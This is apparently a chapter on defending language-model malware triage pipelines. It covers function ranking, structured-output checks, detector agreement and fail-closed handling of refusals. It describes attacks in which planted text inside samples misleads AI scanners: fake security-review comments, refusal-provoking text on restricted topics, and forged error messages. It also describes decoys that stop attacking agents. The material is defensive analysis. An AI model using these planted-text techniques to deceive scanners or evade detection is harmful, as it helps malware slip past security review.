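A large program may not fit in the context window even after filtering, and models already miss much of the malware in very large scripts. If the pipeline sends only the beginning, the attacker can put harmless code there. TRIAGE-CPG, which Sava and colleagues built for Windows programs, instead chooses functions from anywhere in the program.

After decompiling the program, ordinary software maps which functions call which others. It gives each function a score before any model reads the code:

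Score = 0.50 × B + 0.25 × P + 0.25 × L

B is 1 if the function calls a system function and is at an edge of the map, meaning that no other function in the program calls it or that it calls none of them. Otherwise B is 0. P measures how prominent the function is as a caller of others, using the PageRank method that Google developed for web pages. L is the logarithm of the function's length divided by the logarithm of the length of the program's longest function. Persuasive prose doesn't directly affect B or P, but extra text in the decompiled code could increase L.

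The software selects the top tenth of the functions, with a minimum of ten (if the program has that many) and a maximum of 75. The model reads each one separately and records what it does, how suspicious it seems and what innocent explanations there might be. An agent can then follow calls through the program and choose up to 30 more functions to read. Finally, a reporting agent classifies the program as benign, suspicious or malicious from the accumulated notes, without access to new code.

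Sava and colleagues compared eight models on 600 programs, half of them malware. The best, Gemini 3.1 Pro, flagged or escalated 77% of the malware and cleared 94% of the harmless programs. The 77% includes malware that the model called only "suspicious." Both figures come from a single run with metadata included. The researchers had chosen the pipeline's settings using other programs and a cheaper model, so they did not tune it to this test.

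Other models given the same starting functions made very different choices. DeepSeek V4 Pro flagged or escalated 97% of the malware but cleared only a third of the harmless programs. A team with few analysts could hardly use this model, but one that can send every doubtful program to a sandbox might prefer it.

The even split between malware and harmless files also makes the analysts' queue look better than it would be in practice. If 1% of 10,000 incoming files were malware, Gemini 3.1 Pro, at the same rates, would flag or escalate about 77 malicious files and 620 harmless ones, and clear the other 23 malicious ones. The test set also left out programs flagged by one to nine antivirus engines, which are probably the hardest to judge.

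### How much the ranking helps

The ranking formula itself was only modestly better than simpler ways to choose functions. The researchers compared the methods on 200 other programs with the exploring agent switched off, scoring each by the average of the share of malware caught and the share of harmless programs cleared. The formula scored 77.5%, choosing the longest functions scored 76.5%, and random choice averaged 72.4%. The formula's main advantage was that it caught more malware (92%), but it also raised more false alarms.

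This preference was sensible because the exploring agent mostly corrected false alarms. Across nine configurations, exploration improved the verdict on 30 harmless programs and worsened it on 11, but it brought no consistent gain on malware. If the starting functions contained nothing suspicious, the agent had nothing to guide its exploration.

Reading more code didn't reliably help either. With exploration off, the average score rose from 69% with ten starting functions to 81% with 25, then fell to 72% with 150. Large programs needed more functions than small ones and remained difficult. Gemini 3.1 Pro labelled 78% of the malware in the smallest fifth of files malicious, but only 33% in the largest fifth. It also struggled with packed programs and installers, which made up 29% of the malware but 54% of the malware it cleared.

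Sava and colleagues did not test TRIAGE-CPG against planted text, and state that it assumes honest input. Its design would probably stop some attacks anyway. The models receive selected functions and metadata, not a list of every string, so a false product description in an unused section might never reach them. Text that a selected function uses would still reach the models, and forged metadata could too. A note about one function could also pass a false claim to the reporting agent.

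An attacker who knows the formula could add harmless functions that score highly and crowd the harmful ones out of the starting set. Choosing some of the functions at random would make this attack less reliable. The full pipeline missed 13 of 100 malicious programs with random choice and 11 with the formula, although the random result was the best of five random selections.

### Splitting the file instead

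A pipeline can split the whole file into pieces and send the model all of them instead of selecting parts. With TRIAGE-CPG, by contrast, a model reads at most 105 functions, about 0.2% of the largest program in the collection.

Splitting a script into pieces means more requests and more false alarms. A 3-megabyte script contains roughly 750,000 tokens, or 30 pieces of 25,000 tokens, and the operator pays to send the instructions with each piece. If a model wrongly flagged 2% of harmless pieces, independently each time, it would raise at least one false alarm on about 45% of harmless scripts of that size. Liu and colleagues tried splitting long documents for detectors of planted text, counting a document as an attack if any piece triggered an alarm. They found that splitting didn't resolve the trade-off between misses and false alarms.

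Splitting can also separate lines that look suspicious only together. If one piece of the install script downloads a file and another runs it, a model that reads the pieces separately may find both acceptable. Overlapping the pieces helps when the lines are close together, and splitting between functions keeps each function whole. To connect lines that are far apart, the pipeline needs another step that combines the findings from each piece.

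## Checking the model's structured output against independent evidence

Some misleading text will probably get past any filter. Ordinary software can still restrict the form of the model's answer, compare its content with the sample, and compare the verdict with the results of other detectors.

### A schema for the install script

A schema lists the fields that an answer must contain and the values that each field may take. For the five-line version of the install script, an operator might use this one, written in simplified form:

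```
behaviours: a list, each entry with
    type:  downloads_file | starts_program | reads_passwords | sends_data
    line:  whole number
verdict: benign | suspicious | malicious | unknown
```

A good answer would list a download on line 4 and a program start on line 5, followed by "suspicious" or "malicious". The "unknown" value matters because a model always tries to fit the schema and may invent values when the input doesn't suit it, as OpenAI's *Structured outputs* warns.

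If the operator only asks for this format in the prompt, the model may still add a sentence or misspell a field. Constrained decoding prevents that. A language model gives every possible next token a probability. Before the model picks one, software sets the probability of each token that would break the schema to zero and scales up the rest:

New probability = old probability ÷ Z

Z is the total probability of the tokens that the schema allows at that point. Suppose that at the verdict field the model assigns 50% to "malicious", 20% to "suspicious", 10% to "benign", 10% to "unknown" and 10% to other words. Z is then 0.9, and dividing by it raises "malicious" to about 56% and "benign" to about 11%. The relative probabilities of the four verdicts don't change.

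The order of the fields also matters. OpenAI's service fills them in schema order, so putting the behaviours first makes the model list its evidence before it gives a verdict. According to Anthropic's *Structured outputs*, its service does not enforce number ranges, so a model could cite line 52 of a five-line file. The service also doesn't guarantee that capitalisation will match the schema. A pipeline that blocks only the exact word "malicious" might therefore let through a file that the model labelled "Malicious", so Anthropic advises developers to ignore capitalisation when they compare values.

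Like the restricted answers in Jacob and colleagues' design, the model's structured output has no room for a sentence that could carry planted text to a later model or program. But *Inference for Reasoning Models* (2026) notes that a schema controls the shape of an output, not its intent. A misled model can still return an empty list of behaviours and the verdict "benign".

### Do strict formats reduce accuracy or hide refusals?

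*The Format Tax* (Lee, D'Antoni and Berg-Kirkpatrick, 2026) measured how much strict output formats reduce performance on mathematics, science, logic puzzles and writing. For six open models, asking for a format lowered accuracy by 3.9 percentage points on average, and enforcing it lowered accuracy by another 1.6. Three newer commercial models lost almost no accuracy with JSON. Even when the service enforced the format, their largest loss on any of the three reasoning tasks was two points.

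Nguyen, Silva and colleagues (2026) prove in *Constrained Decoding* that enforcement alone can't make the correct answer less likely if the prompt and the model's reasoning stay the same and the schema allows that answer. This follows from the formula above because Z is at most 1, and dividing by it can't reduce a probability. When the evidence is insufficient, the correct answer is "unknown", so a schema without that option fails the last condition.

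The condition about reasoning may explain some worse results. *Inference for Reasoning Models* reports that schema enforcement lowered Llama 3.1 8B's score by 25.3 points but Qwen3 8B's by only 1.2. In *Capacity, Not Format* (2026), GPT-4o mini solved 60% of hard mathematics problems when it could reason in ordinary text first, 51% when it had to answer in JSON, and 10% when it had to reply through a function call, which left no room for written reasoning. The remedy is to let the model reason freely and apply the schema only to its final answer. Lee and colleagues found that this recovered most of the lost accuracy, and Anthropic's service leaves the model's thinking unconstrained by default.

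A schema may also make a model less likely to choose "unknown", even when the schema allows it. *Repair, Not Improvement* (Janghoon Lee, 2026) tested three small Qwen3 models by having them choose from ten tools or "None" for requests that none of the tools suited. Constrained answers were correct less often than free ones in four of six combinations of model and language, by up to 29.5 points, even though the schema allowed "None". The largest of the three models lost about nine points in English and none in Korean. These models are much smaller than those in most triage pipelines, but a team that uses a small model for first screening should check how often it returns "unknown" with and without the schema. None of these studies used malware, so the team should also compare accuracy on its own samples.

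Some strict output formats still let a pipeline detect refusals, provided its programmers check for them. OpenAI's service reports a refusal in a separate field, and Anthropic's lets a refusal override the schema. But an open model running under a strict grammar must produce one of the four verdicts even when its training would have led it to refuse, and the operator can't tell that verdict from a real judgement.

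### Checking the evidence that the model cites

Once the answer has the right form, software can look up each cited location. For the install script, whose first line is the comment about a security review, the checks might work like this:

| Part of the answer | What the software finds | What it does |
|---|---|---|
| Downloads a file, line 4 | Line 4 is code and calls a download function | Accepts the claim |
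| Reads passwords, line 52 | The file has five lines | Rejects the claim and escalates the file |
| Sends data, line 1 | Line 1 is a comment | Rejects the claim and escalates the file |
| Verdict "benign" | The software has accepted a download and a program start | Overrides the verdict and escalates the file |

For a compiled program, the model would cite a function's address or a string's position instead of a line. The software has to check both that the cited location exists and what kind of text is there, because a model that cites the attacker's comment as proof of a security review may still be quoting it accurately.

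When a claim fails the check, the software should escalate the file rather than drop the claim. If it dropped the claim, an attacker could try to make the model attach a true alarm to the wrong line so that the check would remove the alarm. Escalation adds some work whenever the model miscounts lines.

Some malware-analysis systems already include checks of this kind. *LCC-LLM* (2026) compares a model's finished report with evidence from reverse-engineering tools to catch invented indicators and unsupported claims about who wrote the malware. In Microsoft's *Project Ire*, every claim refers to a function, behaviour or artifact that the agent observed. In one example from Microsoft, the agent correctly identified that a program shuts down antivirus software, but also took another function for a defence against debugging. The validator flagged the second claim as unsupported, and the final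 report described it as unconfirmed. The verdict was right regardless, and Microsoft doesn't report how often the validator catches errors that would have changed a verdict.

Citations can support only claims that a program does something, because no line shows that it does nothing harmful. If planted text leads the model to leave out the download and the program start, the empty list passes every check in the table. The software therefore needs to gather evidence without the model. In this script, a parser can find the calls to `download` and `start`, and a fixed rule can then forbid a benign verdict. Another rule can enforce the labels that Choi and colleagues propose for claims about a program's maker.

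### Scoring the model's claims with fixed rules

In *MARS*, Choi tested a design that takes the verdict away from the model. The model lists claims about a program, gives each a category and a severity from 1 to 5, and ordinary software computes a score:

Score = sum over all claims of (category weight × severity multiplier)

Each of the eleven categories has a weight, such as 2.2 for suspicious system calls, 1.8 for commands, 1.0 for network indicators and −1.5 for signs that the program is harmless. The multiplier rises from 0.55 for severity 1 to 1.5 for severity 5. A score below a threshold *t* gives "benign", a score of at least 2*t* gives "malicious", and anything between gives "suspicious". Choi set *t* separately for each model using 197 other programs.

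*MARS* handles only compiled programs, but its calculation can be illustrated with the install script. A network indicator of severity 3 contributes 1.0 × 1.0, and a command of severity 4 contributes 1.8 × 1.25, for a total of 3.25. This is above GLM-5.2's threshold of 3.025, so the rule classifies the script as suspicious. If the comment leads the model to add a sign of harmlessness with severity 3, that subtracts 1.5, lowering the score to 1.75, and the rule classifies the script as benign. The comment can change the verdict even though the rule is fixed, because the model supplies the rule's inputs.

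Choi compared this method with asking the same model for a verdict directly. Both methods were given the same evidence on 1,195 Windows and Linux programs, about half of them malware. In the table, both "suspicious" and "malicious" count as correct for malware.

| Model | Accuracy, direct verdict | Accuracy, scored claims |
|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 94.0% | 73.1% |
| DeepSeek V4 Pro | 89.8% | 86.1% |
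| GLM-5.2 | 96.8% | 85.3% |
| Gemma 4 31B | 90.9% | 85.2% |
| GPT-OSS-20B | 86.7% | 71.5% |
| Qwen3.5 397B | 99.7% | 90.6% |

The direct verdict was better for every model and cheaper for five of the six. The high figures are weak evidence that the models understand behaviour well, because a simple classifier that used only a program's processor type, size, randomness, packing and signature did slightly better on the Windows programs than the models' direct verdicts on average. But direct verdicts were also better on the 300 programs that were hardest for this classifier.

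Choi then altered the stored evidence for 182 programs in four ways and reran three of the models. The figures are changes in the share of malware flagged, in percentage points.

| Change to the evidence | Fixed rules without a model | Direct verdict | Scored claims |
|---|---|---|---|
| Indicators removed | −34.1 | −10.0 | −29.2 |
| Harmless-looking material added | 0 | −4.4 | +0.4 |
| Instruction-like text added | 0 | +3.0 | −1.5 |
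| Much unrelated material added | 0 | +3.0 | +3.7 |

Removing the indicators reduced detection by scored claims almost as much as detection by the fixed rules, which fell to zero. Among the other changes, only the 4.4-point fall is clearly larger than chance would explain. Harmless-looking material did not lower detection by scored claims on average, so the weakness in the install-script example may be rare in practice, or the material may have been unpersuasive. Instruction-like text greatly reduced Gemini 2.5 Flash's detection under claim scoring, which the average across models does not show.

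These results are evidence against letting a formula replace the model's verdict, but the study did not test checking claims against the sample. In part of the study, a second call to the model labeled claims as supported or unsupported, but the scoring rule did not use the labels. Choi's full system also validates references to evidence, and that validation remains untested.

Stored claims let an operator recompute verdicts without calling a model again. Choi reproduced 9,456 old verdicts exactly from stored claims, including 2,366 from two models that their provider had since withdrawn. A different scoring rule agreed with the original on only half of the labels. An operator who discovers that attackers have been planting signs of harmlessness could set the weight of those signs to zero, choose a new threshold and rescore every old file.

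### Agreement among detectors

A pipeline can also compare the model's verdict with the results of detectors that examine different evidence. Reputation data, for example, records how long a file or web address has been in circulation and whether anyone has reported it.

| Detector | What it examines | How malware can evade it |
|---|---|---|
| Signature rules | Known patterns of bytes or text | By using new code |
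| Sandbox run | Behaviour during a short run | By waiting, or by recognising the sandbox |
| Reputation data | The history of a file or address | By using a new file and a new address |
| Second model | Usually the same evidence as the first model | By using text that misleads both models |

A second model is the easiest to add, and its value is the easiest to overestimate. Suppose 1,000 malicious files go to two models, each of which misses 10%. The share that both miss is:

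P(both miss) = P(first misses) × P(second misses, given that the first missed)

If two models each miss 100 of 1,000 files and their errors are independent, the second model misses ten of the 100 files that the first one missed, so together they miss 1% of the total. If the second model misses 60 of those 100, together they miss 6%. If both miss the same 100 files, the second model adds nothing.

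Planted text can make two models miss the same files even when their mistakes are otherwise unrelated. Suppose 100 of 1,000 files contain planted text, and each model misses 55 of those and 5% of the other 900. Each model then misses 100 files, or 10%. If their errors were independent, both models would miss about 1% of the files. Instead, they both miss about two of the ordinary files, plus about 30 of the files with planted text if chance decides which ones mislead each model, or 55 if the same ones mislead both. The total is 3% to 6% of all files. An attacker who finds a text that works on both models can put it in every sample, which raises the total further.

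Models' errors also overlap without any attacker. *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (Kim, Garg and colleagues, 2025) compared 71 models on multiple-choice questions. When two models were both wrong, they chose the same wrong answer 60% of the time, compared with 33% for random choice, and the overlap was greater between more accurate models. In *Do Large Language Models Know Colombian Law?* (2026), a majority vote of 15 models scored 84.3%, below the best single model's 90.5%. These studies measure agreement on one wrong answer among several, so their percentages can't be used directly in the formula above. *The Oracle's Fingerprint* (2026) provides a closer measure, an average correlation of 0.77 between the forecasting errors of GPT-4o, Claude and Gemini. None of these studies measured overlap on malware, but if misses in malware triage were that strongly correlated, two models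 that each miss 10% of malicious samples would both miss about 8% of them.

The best evidence for using a second model comes from the experiment with false product descriptions, where only Gemini 2.5 Pro classified any of the 35 altered Windows programs as benign. A pipeline that required all three models to agree before clearing a file would have cleared none of them. But the attacker did not adapt the text to the other two models. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026) describes a public competition with 464 participants. Attacks that beat the most robust models also worked on other models 44% to 81% of the time, while attacks on weak models rarely worked on stronger ones. A weak second model therefore adds little protection against an attacker who has tested attacks on a strong one.

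Giving the second detector different evidence should help more than choosing a different model. The detector could read the code without comments or unused strings, or only the record of a sandbox run. Choi added sandbox records for 20 selected programs, but the benefit is uncertain. The number of malicious programs flagged by scored claims rose from five to seven out of seven for Windows but fell from six to five out of seven for Linux.

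Ordinary tools need testing too. The fixed rules in *MARS* raised an alert on 40 of 300 harmless Linux programs and on none of the 298 malicious ones. The YARA rules included none for Linux malware, and a bonus meant for dangerous combinations of functions went mostly to harmless programs. Using these rules to veto benign verdicts on the Linux files would have created 40 false alarms and detected no malware.

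### A model that may not clear a file alone

Willison and Bista's principle implies that a model may raise suspicion about a file but never clear it alone. This rule would limit the damage from all these errors. The system could clear a file if its hash is on a list of known releases, or if it has a valid signature from a trusted company and its behaviour breaks no fixed rule.

*The Hitchhiker's Guide to Program Analysis, Part III* (Li, Zhou and colleagues, 2026), a study of warnings about bugs in Android drivers, gives the clearest argument for treating confirmation and dismissal differently. One run of the program that triggers a bug is enough to confirm it, but dismissing the warning requires ruling out every such run, which a plausible explanation can't do. In one case, a check just above the suspect line seemed to limit a number to 16, but a large negative number could pass the check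 and then become positive when the program stored it in a smaller format. Both an earlier language-model filter and a human reviewer had missed the bug.

In EVIDENT, a model writes a small test program around the suspect code, other software checks that the program hasn't excluded the dangerous inputs, and a conventional analyser then decides whether the warning is real. On 200 warnings, 40 of them real bugs, EVIDENT dismissed between 49% and 64% of the false alarms, depending on the model, and no real bugs. When GPT-5.5 made the final decision instead, overall accuracy was 2 to 5.5 points higher and at most 29 more false alarms were dismissed, but so were 11 to 18 of the 40 real bugs.

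That comparison supports the rule well, but malware triage has no equivalent of the analyser. Software can prove that a number stays within a limit, but Microsoft points out that no program can compute whether software is malicious. Many harmless files will therefore lack independent evidence strong enough to clear them, and somebody has to examine those files.

Not letting the model clear files can add a lot of work for analysts. Take the earlier example of 10,000 incoming files, 100 of them malicious. Suppose they arrive in one day, and lists of known releases and valid signatures clear 70% of the harmless ones. That leaves 2,970 harmless files and the 100 malicious ones. If Gemini 3.1 Pro is allowed to clear files, at the same rates as before, about 255 go to analysts, who need 43 hours at ten minutes each, and 23 malicious files get through. If the model isn't allowed to clear any, all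 3,070 files go to analysts and take 512 hours. The team works about 20 extra hours for each additional malicious file it catches, even on the generous assumption that ten minutes is enough to recognise one.

A queue twelve times as long could cause some of the misses that the rule is meant to prevent, because tired analysts make mistakes too. Microsoft lists alert fatigue among its reasons for building Project Ire.

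To save analysts' time, the pipeline could send files the model labels benign to a sandbox instead of a person, which means about 2,800 runs a day in the example. Choi's tests with sandbox records typically took three to four minutes each, and at four minutes, eight machines running around the clock could handle the load. The pipeline would clear a file only if the model and the sandbox both found nothing. Malware that carries planted text and stays inactive until the sandbox run ends would still get through, but its author would have to defeat two detectors that examine different things. A team without enough sandboxes could use the model's verdict to decide which files analysts see first, provided that the lowest-priority files stay on hold until someone checks them.

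## Monitoring refusals, errors and missing verdicts

None of these checks can run if the model returns no verdict. The model may refuse, its provider's filter may block the request, or the reply may arrive late, cut off or garbled. The Hades packages, macOS.Gaslight and GuardBreaker seem to rely on such a failure. An operator can deny attackers the benefit by holding every file without a verdict. Failures are also useful evidence, because a sudden run of refusals may mean someone is planting text to cause them.

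### How reliably text in the data can stop a model

Researchers described the effect before it appeared in malware. *LLM Safeguard is a Double-Edged Sword* (2024) considers an attacker who adds text to other people's requests so that a service refuses them. *Hoist with His Own Petard* (2025) considers an attacker who causes refusals by planting documents in a collection that a model searches for answers.

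The largest measured effect comes from a defensive use of the trick. Tracebit, a company that sells decoys for catching intruders, gave five models the role of an attacker in an Amazon cloud account with about 300 resources and ten deliberate routes of attack. In some runs the account also held a decoy secret, which contained a short text on a subject that AI providers restrict. Tracebit's *Context Bombs* (2026) gives these averages across the five models:

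| Result of the run | No decoy | Decoy with planted text |
|---|---|---|
| Agent gained full administrator access | 57% | 5% |
| Agent gained that access and a lasting foothold | 36% | 1% |
| Agent completed at least one route of attack | 91% | 15% |

Claude Opus 4.8 gained administrator access in 93% of runs without the decoy and in none with it. Tracebit scored 152 runs, about 15 per model in each condition, so the model's true success rate with the decoy could be as high as about 18%.

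Tracebit sells the product it tested, and it chose the texts by trying many candidates on agents and keeping those that worked. Its comparison runs had no decoy, so some agents may have stopped because they recognised a trap, not because of the text in the decoy. However, that is very unlikely to explain a drop from 93% to zero.

The candidate texts that Tracebit discarded matter more for triage. Most texts that provoked a refusal in a short prompt no longer did so once an agent had read tens of thousands of tokens of other material. When a scanner sends a model a 40-line script in a single request, the model reads almost nothing else, so a text too weak to stop Tracebit's agents might still stop the scanner. Tracebit did not test scanners, but a malware author could run the same search against any public model.

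The subject that stopped a model also depended on the provider. Text about dangerous biology stopped the leading Western models, and text on subjects that are politically sensitive in China stopped Chinese models run by Chinese companies. Schneier points out in *Hiding Prompt Injection in Legal Filing* that the method works only on models with guardrails.

### Refusals that nobody provoked

Models also refuse legitimate security work, which makes refusals caused by an attacker's text harder to spot. *Defensive Refusal Bias* (Campbell, Kale and colleagues, 2026) analysed 2,390 requests that student teams had made while defending computers in an American competition. The models refused 30.5% of the requests containing terms such as "exploit" or "payload" and 11.2% of the rest. They refused 34.3% of malware-analysis requests and none of the log-analysis requests.

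These rates are a poor forecast for a pipeline in late 2026. The models (Claude 3.5 Sonnet, GPT-4o and Llama 3.3 70B) date from 2024, and the count of refusals includes vague answers that avoided useful detail. Judging by the overall refusal rate of 12.2%, only about 120 requests contained the offensive terms. Those requests were different from the ones without such terms and may have concerned more sensitive work, although Campbell and colleagues call the two groups equivalent in meaning. A classifier given only whether a request contained offensive terms or a claim of authorisation predicted refusals barely better than chance, while one that used the meaning of the whole request did much better. Removing a few words from the operator's prompt would therefore probably not reduce refusals much.

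Newer models still refuse such work, at widely varying rates. In *Choose your fighter* (2026), Cisco Talos had models from Anthropic and OpenAI examine 80,054 simulated log records and decide whether they were real. Claude Sonnet 5 had no refusals or blocks at its low and medium reasoning settings, one at high, four at the next setting and five at the maximum. Safeguards blocked 21 of 31 attempts with Anthropic's Fable, so Talos left it out of the main comparison.

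The problem has already disrupted a real investigation. In July 2026 an AI agent broke into Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets, and left a log of more than 17,000 events. According to Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (2026), commercial providers blocked the analysis because the log contained real attack commands. *OpenAI Models Hack Hugging Face* names the models involved as Claude Opus and Fable. The company's staff completed the work with GLM-5.2, an open model, on their own machines. Campbell and colleagues' students had no trouble with log analysis, but they were asking older models for help. Hugging Face was also submitting the attacker's commands in bulk, which is closer to what a triage pipeline does.

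### Vetted access for security teams

Providers now relax some safeguards for security teams whose identity and purpose they have verified. OpenAI's *Scaling Trusted Access for Cyber with GPT‑5.5 and GPT‑5.5‑Cyber* (2026) promises approved users fewer classifier refusals on work including malware analysis and reverse engineering. OpenAI still blocks requests to steal passwords or deploy malware. Anthropic's *Cyber Verification Program* (2026) has three levels of access and warns that Anthropic's classifiers may interrupt malware analysis by customers outside the programme.

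Approval is tied to the account, which is an advantage over claiming authorisation in the prompt. In Campbell and colleagues' data, models refused 21.8% of requests that claimed authorisation and 11.6% of those that didn't. When the researchers removed the claim from the same requests, the refusal rate fell to 13.7%. Anyone can make such a claim, and models may have learned to associate it with attempts to get around their rules. Irregular's *Same Request, Different Outcome* gives an example in which stated intent alone decided whether three frontier models complied with a technical request, and argues for judging the technical content instead.

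Vetted access should reduce refusals caused by the ordinary contents of malware. It probably does little against text planted to cause a refusal, because whoever plants it can choose a subject unrelated to computers. Tracebit had an exemption from Anthropic's cybersecurity restrictions for Opus 4.8, but text about biology still stopped the model. GuardBreaker's request for help with a nuclear weapon also falls outside any cybersecurity exemption. Some blocks remain even within cybersecurity. An earlier Anthropic page, *Real-time cyber safeguards on Claude Opus and Sonnet*, lists uses, such as writing ransomware, that the ordinary application could not unlock.

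Even an approved account may not get a usable model. Talos's account was in Anthropic's programme when Fable blocked two thirds of its attempts, though Anthropic reorganised the programme that October. Companies that sell scanners cannot yet apply to Anthropic to use this access inside their products. OpenAI has a partner programme that allows this, according to Axios' *OpenAI rolls out more capable version of cyber model* (2026). Anthropic can also narrow or withdraw its approval, which could suddenly raise a pipeline's refusal rate without any attack.

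### A code for each kind of failure

A pipeline that logs every failure as "error" can't tell a provider's outage from a wave of hostile files. It needs at least six codes:

| Code | Where the software finds it | First response |
|---|---|---|
| Refusal | The refusal field, or the text of the reply | New request with filtered input |
| Provider block | An error type or stop reason sent by the provider | New request with filtered input, or another model |
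| Timeout | The pipeline's own clock | Same request once more |
| Truncation | A stop reason showing that the reply hit its length limit, or the evidence builder's record of what it left out | Higher limit, or a split file |
| Malformed output | The schema check | Same request once more |
| Low confidence | The confidence field | Another detector |

Truncation can affect either the model's reply or its input. If the reply is cut off, the verdict is usually missing. If the evidence builder cut the input, the model can still return a well-formed verdict even though it received only part of the file, and the verdict will not show that anything was left out.

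Refusals in free text are hard to recognise by their wording. In *You Shouldn't Have Asked* (2026), 72% of GPT-4o's 144 unexplained refusals were identical, but newer models phrased theirs in many ways. A second model can be used to recognise refusals, but a provider's filter blocked the study's judge on some examples. Filing a refusal under "malformed output" makes the statistics less accurate but doesn't make the pipeline less safe, because anything other than a valid verdict counts as missing.

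Low confidence is the weakest of the six signals. When false product descriptions failed to change a model's malicious verdict, its average stated confidence barely changed. An operator should set the confidence threshold using the pipeline's past mistakes, and shouldn't skip other checks because confidence is high.

### Failing closed

The rule for missing verdicts takes three lines, in simplified form:

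```
if status is complete and verdict is benign: continue to the other checks
if status is complete and verdict is not benign: apply the rule for that verdict
in every other case: set verdict to unknown, hold the file, record the code
```

A programmer can break this rule by accident. A program that blocks files labelled "malicious" and releases all others will release a file with an empty verdict. A program that sets the verdict to "benign" by default, and changes it only if the model returns a different one, will also release that file.

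Mistakes like these are common. *When Code Becomes an LLM Call* (Weng, Wang and colleagues, 2026) examined 496 places where 40 popular open-source agents call a model. In 82% of them, the program ran checks both before and after the call, but only 5.3% met all the requirements the researchers derived from the call's purpose. An optional safety check in Gemini CLI, Google's coding agent, returned "allow" when the model call failed or the reply was empty or unreadable. The researchers triggered 38 flaws of various kinds in the running agents, and a small change to the code stopped every one.

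*PolicyGuard* (2026), a filter that keeps confidential data out of requests to coding assistants, has the opposite default: it blocks a request if its classifier takes more than ten seconds, can't be reached, or returns something that isn't a recognised decision. The justification is that a leak can't be undone, whereas a false alarm only annoys a developer. Malware triage has a similar imbalance, though holding files also carries a risk, because a delayed security update can leave machines exposed.

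Failing closed is hardest to sustain during an outage, when every file lacks a verdict. *Countermind* (2025), a proposed security design for language models, includes an intermediate mode for the loss of a less critical component. In triage, such a mode could use known releases, signatures and sandbox runs to clear only the files they would have cleared anyway, and hold the rest. The pipeline should enter this mode only when the model also fails on known test files. Otherwise an attacker could switch off the model for everyone by submitting a few files that make it time out.

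### Retries and escalation

Repeating the same request makes sense after a timeout or a garbled reply, because the fault may be temporary. After a refusal or a block, the same request would still contain the planted text, so the evidence builder should first filter the input, for example by removing comments from a script, and send the result in a new session. PiunikaWeb (2026) reports that once Claude's filter had flagged something in a conversation, it could also reject harmless follow-up messages, so researchers had to start again. A pipeline that judges several samples in one request should also resubmit them separately after a block, because one hostile file could otherwise leave all the others without verdicts.

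Suppose the author of the 40-line install script replaces the false security review with a comment that provokes a refusal. The provider blocks the first request. The evidence builder then removes the comment, and the model describes a script that downloads and starts an unknown program. The pipeline now has a verdict and some evidence that the comment caused the block. Getting the same results when repeating both requests would strengthen that evidence, since refusals can vary between calls.

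If filtered input still yields no verdict, the pipeline can try another model. One from a different provider may have different restrictions, although an attacker can plant several restricted subjects in one file. An open model on the operator's own hardware avoids the provider's filter, and Hugging Face advises companies to test one before they need it. Cisco Talos, in *The safety penalty* (2026), suggests a gateway that detects refusals and automatically reroutes the refused requests to such a model. The team then has to maintain two systems and make sure that both interpret the same request the same way. A fallback may also be easier to deceive than the main model, so the team should test it with false claims and planted instructions as well.

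Retries need a fixed limit and a rule for combining the answers. If each attempt had an independent 10% chance of calling a certain piece of malware benign, a pipeline that made three attempts and accepted any benign verdict would let that malware through about 27% of the time. Keeping the most severe verdict is safer. A benign verdict that follows a refusal shouldn't clear the file by itself, because the filter may have removed evidence along with the planted text. The file could go to a sandbox, and then to an analyst if no independent evidence supports clearing it.

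### Real errors and errors written in the sample

A real system error leaves a record outside the sample. If a disk is full, the operating system returns an error to the program that tried to write to it, and if a session expires, the provider's server rejects the next request. A fake message about either event is only a string that the evidence builder successfully extracted from the sample.

For example, an agent asks a tool for a program's strings, and one of them is a warning that the disk is full. The software that ran the tool recorded that the tool finished normally and returned 412 strings, including the warning. This software can also check the disk itself. It should take the status from its own record and the disk check, and ignore any status in the extracted text or the agent's report. If the agent stops and blames a full disk, the pipeline records an unconfirmed error, starts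 a new session and escalates the file.

Labelling each tool result with its real status may help the agent too, but the model receives the label as text, which an attacker can imitate, so the original record has to stay where only ordinary software can write to it.

The record must also separate blocks from technical faults. In *I'm Sorry Dave, This Request Triggered Restrictions On Violative Cyber Content*, Helton (2026) describes asking Claude Code about new settings in a version-control program and receiving a policy block as an API error. A pipeline that treated every API error as a temporary fault would keep resubmitting such a request and never count it as a block. The software should read the error type from the provider's response rather than search for the words of the error message, since an attacker can put those words in a string in a sample.

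Even when an error is real, the sample may have caused it, because malware authors can build files that crash a decompiler. To check, the pipeline can rerun the sample on another machine alongside a known harmless file. If only the sample fails, something in it probably caused the error. If both fail, the likely cause is a fault in the tool or the service.

### What a refusal says about a file

The value of a refusal as evidence depends on how often harmless files cause one. Take 10,000 incoming files, of which 100 are malicious, and suppose that ten of the malicious files carry text meant to provoke a refusal. The refusal rates here are invented for illustration:

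| Files | Number | Refusal rate | Expected refusals |
|---|---|---|---|
| Harmless | 9,900 | 0.2% | 19.8 |
| Ordinary malware | 90 | 1% | 0.9 |
| Malware with refusal-provoking text | 10 | 60% | 6.0 |
| Total | 10,000 | | 26.7 |

About 7 of the roughly 27 refused files are malicious, or 26%, compared with 1% of all files. A pipeline that fails open would release those 7. One that fails closed could send all 27 to analysts, who would need about four and a half hours at ten minutes a file. Blocking all 27 would be excessive, because about 20 are harmless. The four remaining files with planted text get an ordinary analysis, so the refusal rule doesn't catch them.

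If the model refused 2% of harmless files instead of 0.2%, there would be about 205 refusals, and only 3.4% of them would involve malware. If a model refuses most legitimate work, as Fable did in Talos's test, a refusal is almost no help in telling whether a file is malicious. Vetted access could therefore make monitoring more useful even if it prevented no provoked refusals. If it cut the refusal rates for harmless files and ordinary malware to a quarter, starting from 0.2% for harmless files, and left the 60% rate for malware with refusal-provoking text unchanged, there would be about 11 refusals, and 56% of the refused files would be malicious.

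The example assumes far more planted text than Talos has found. If no files contained planted text and the 1% refusal rate applied to all 100 malicious files, about 5% of refused files would be malicious. That is still five times the share of malicious files overall, but only because the example assumes that models refuse ordinary malware more often than harmless files. An operator can check that assumption by counting how many refused files later turn out to be malicious.

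### Tracking the rates

An overall refusal rate can hide a campaign that uses only one type of file. Suppose 2,000 of the 10,000 daily files are install scripts, and the normal refusal rate is 0.2% both for them and for all files together. That gives an average of four refusals a day among the install scripts and 20 in total. One day there are eight extra refusals, all among the install scripts, which raises those counts to 12 and 28. If refusals occur independently, chance would produce a total of 28 or more on about one day in 19, which is too often to justify an alarm, but it would produce 12 or more among the install scripts on only about one day in 1,100.

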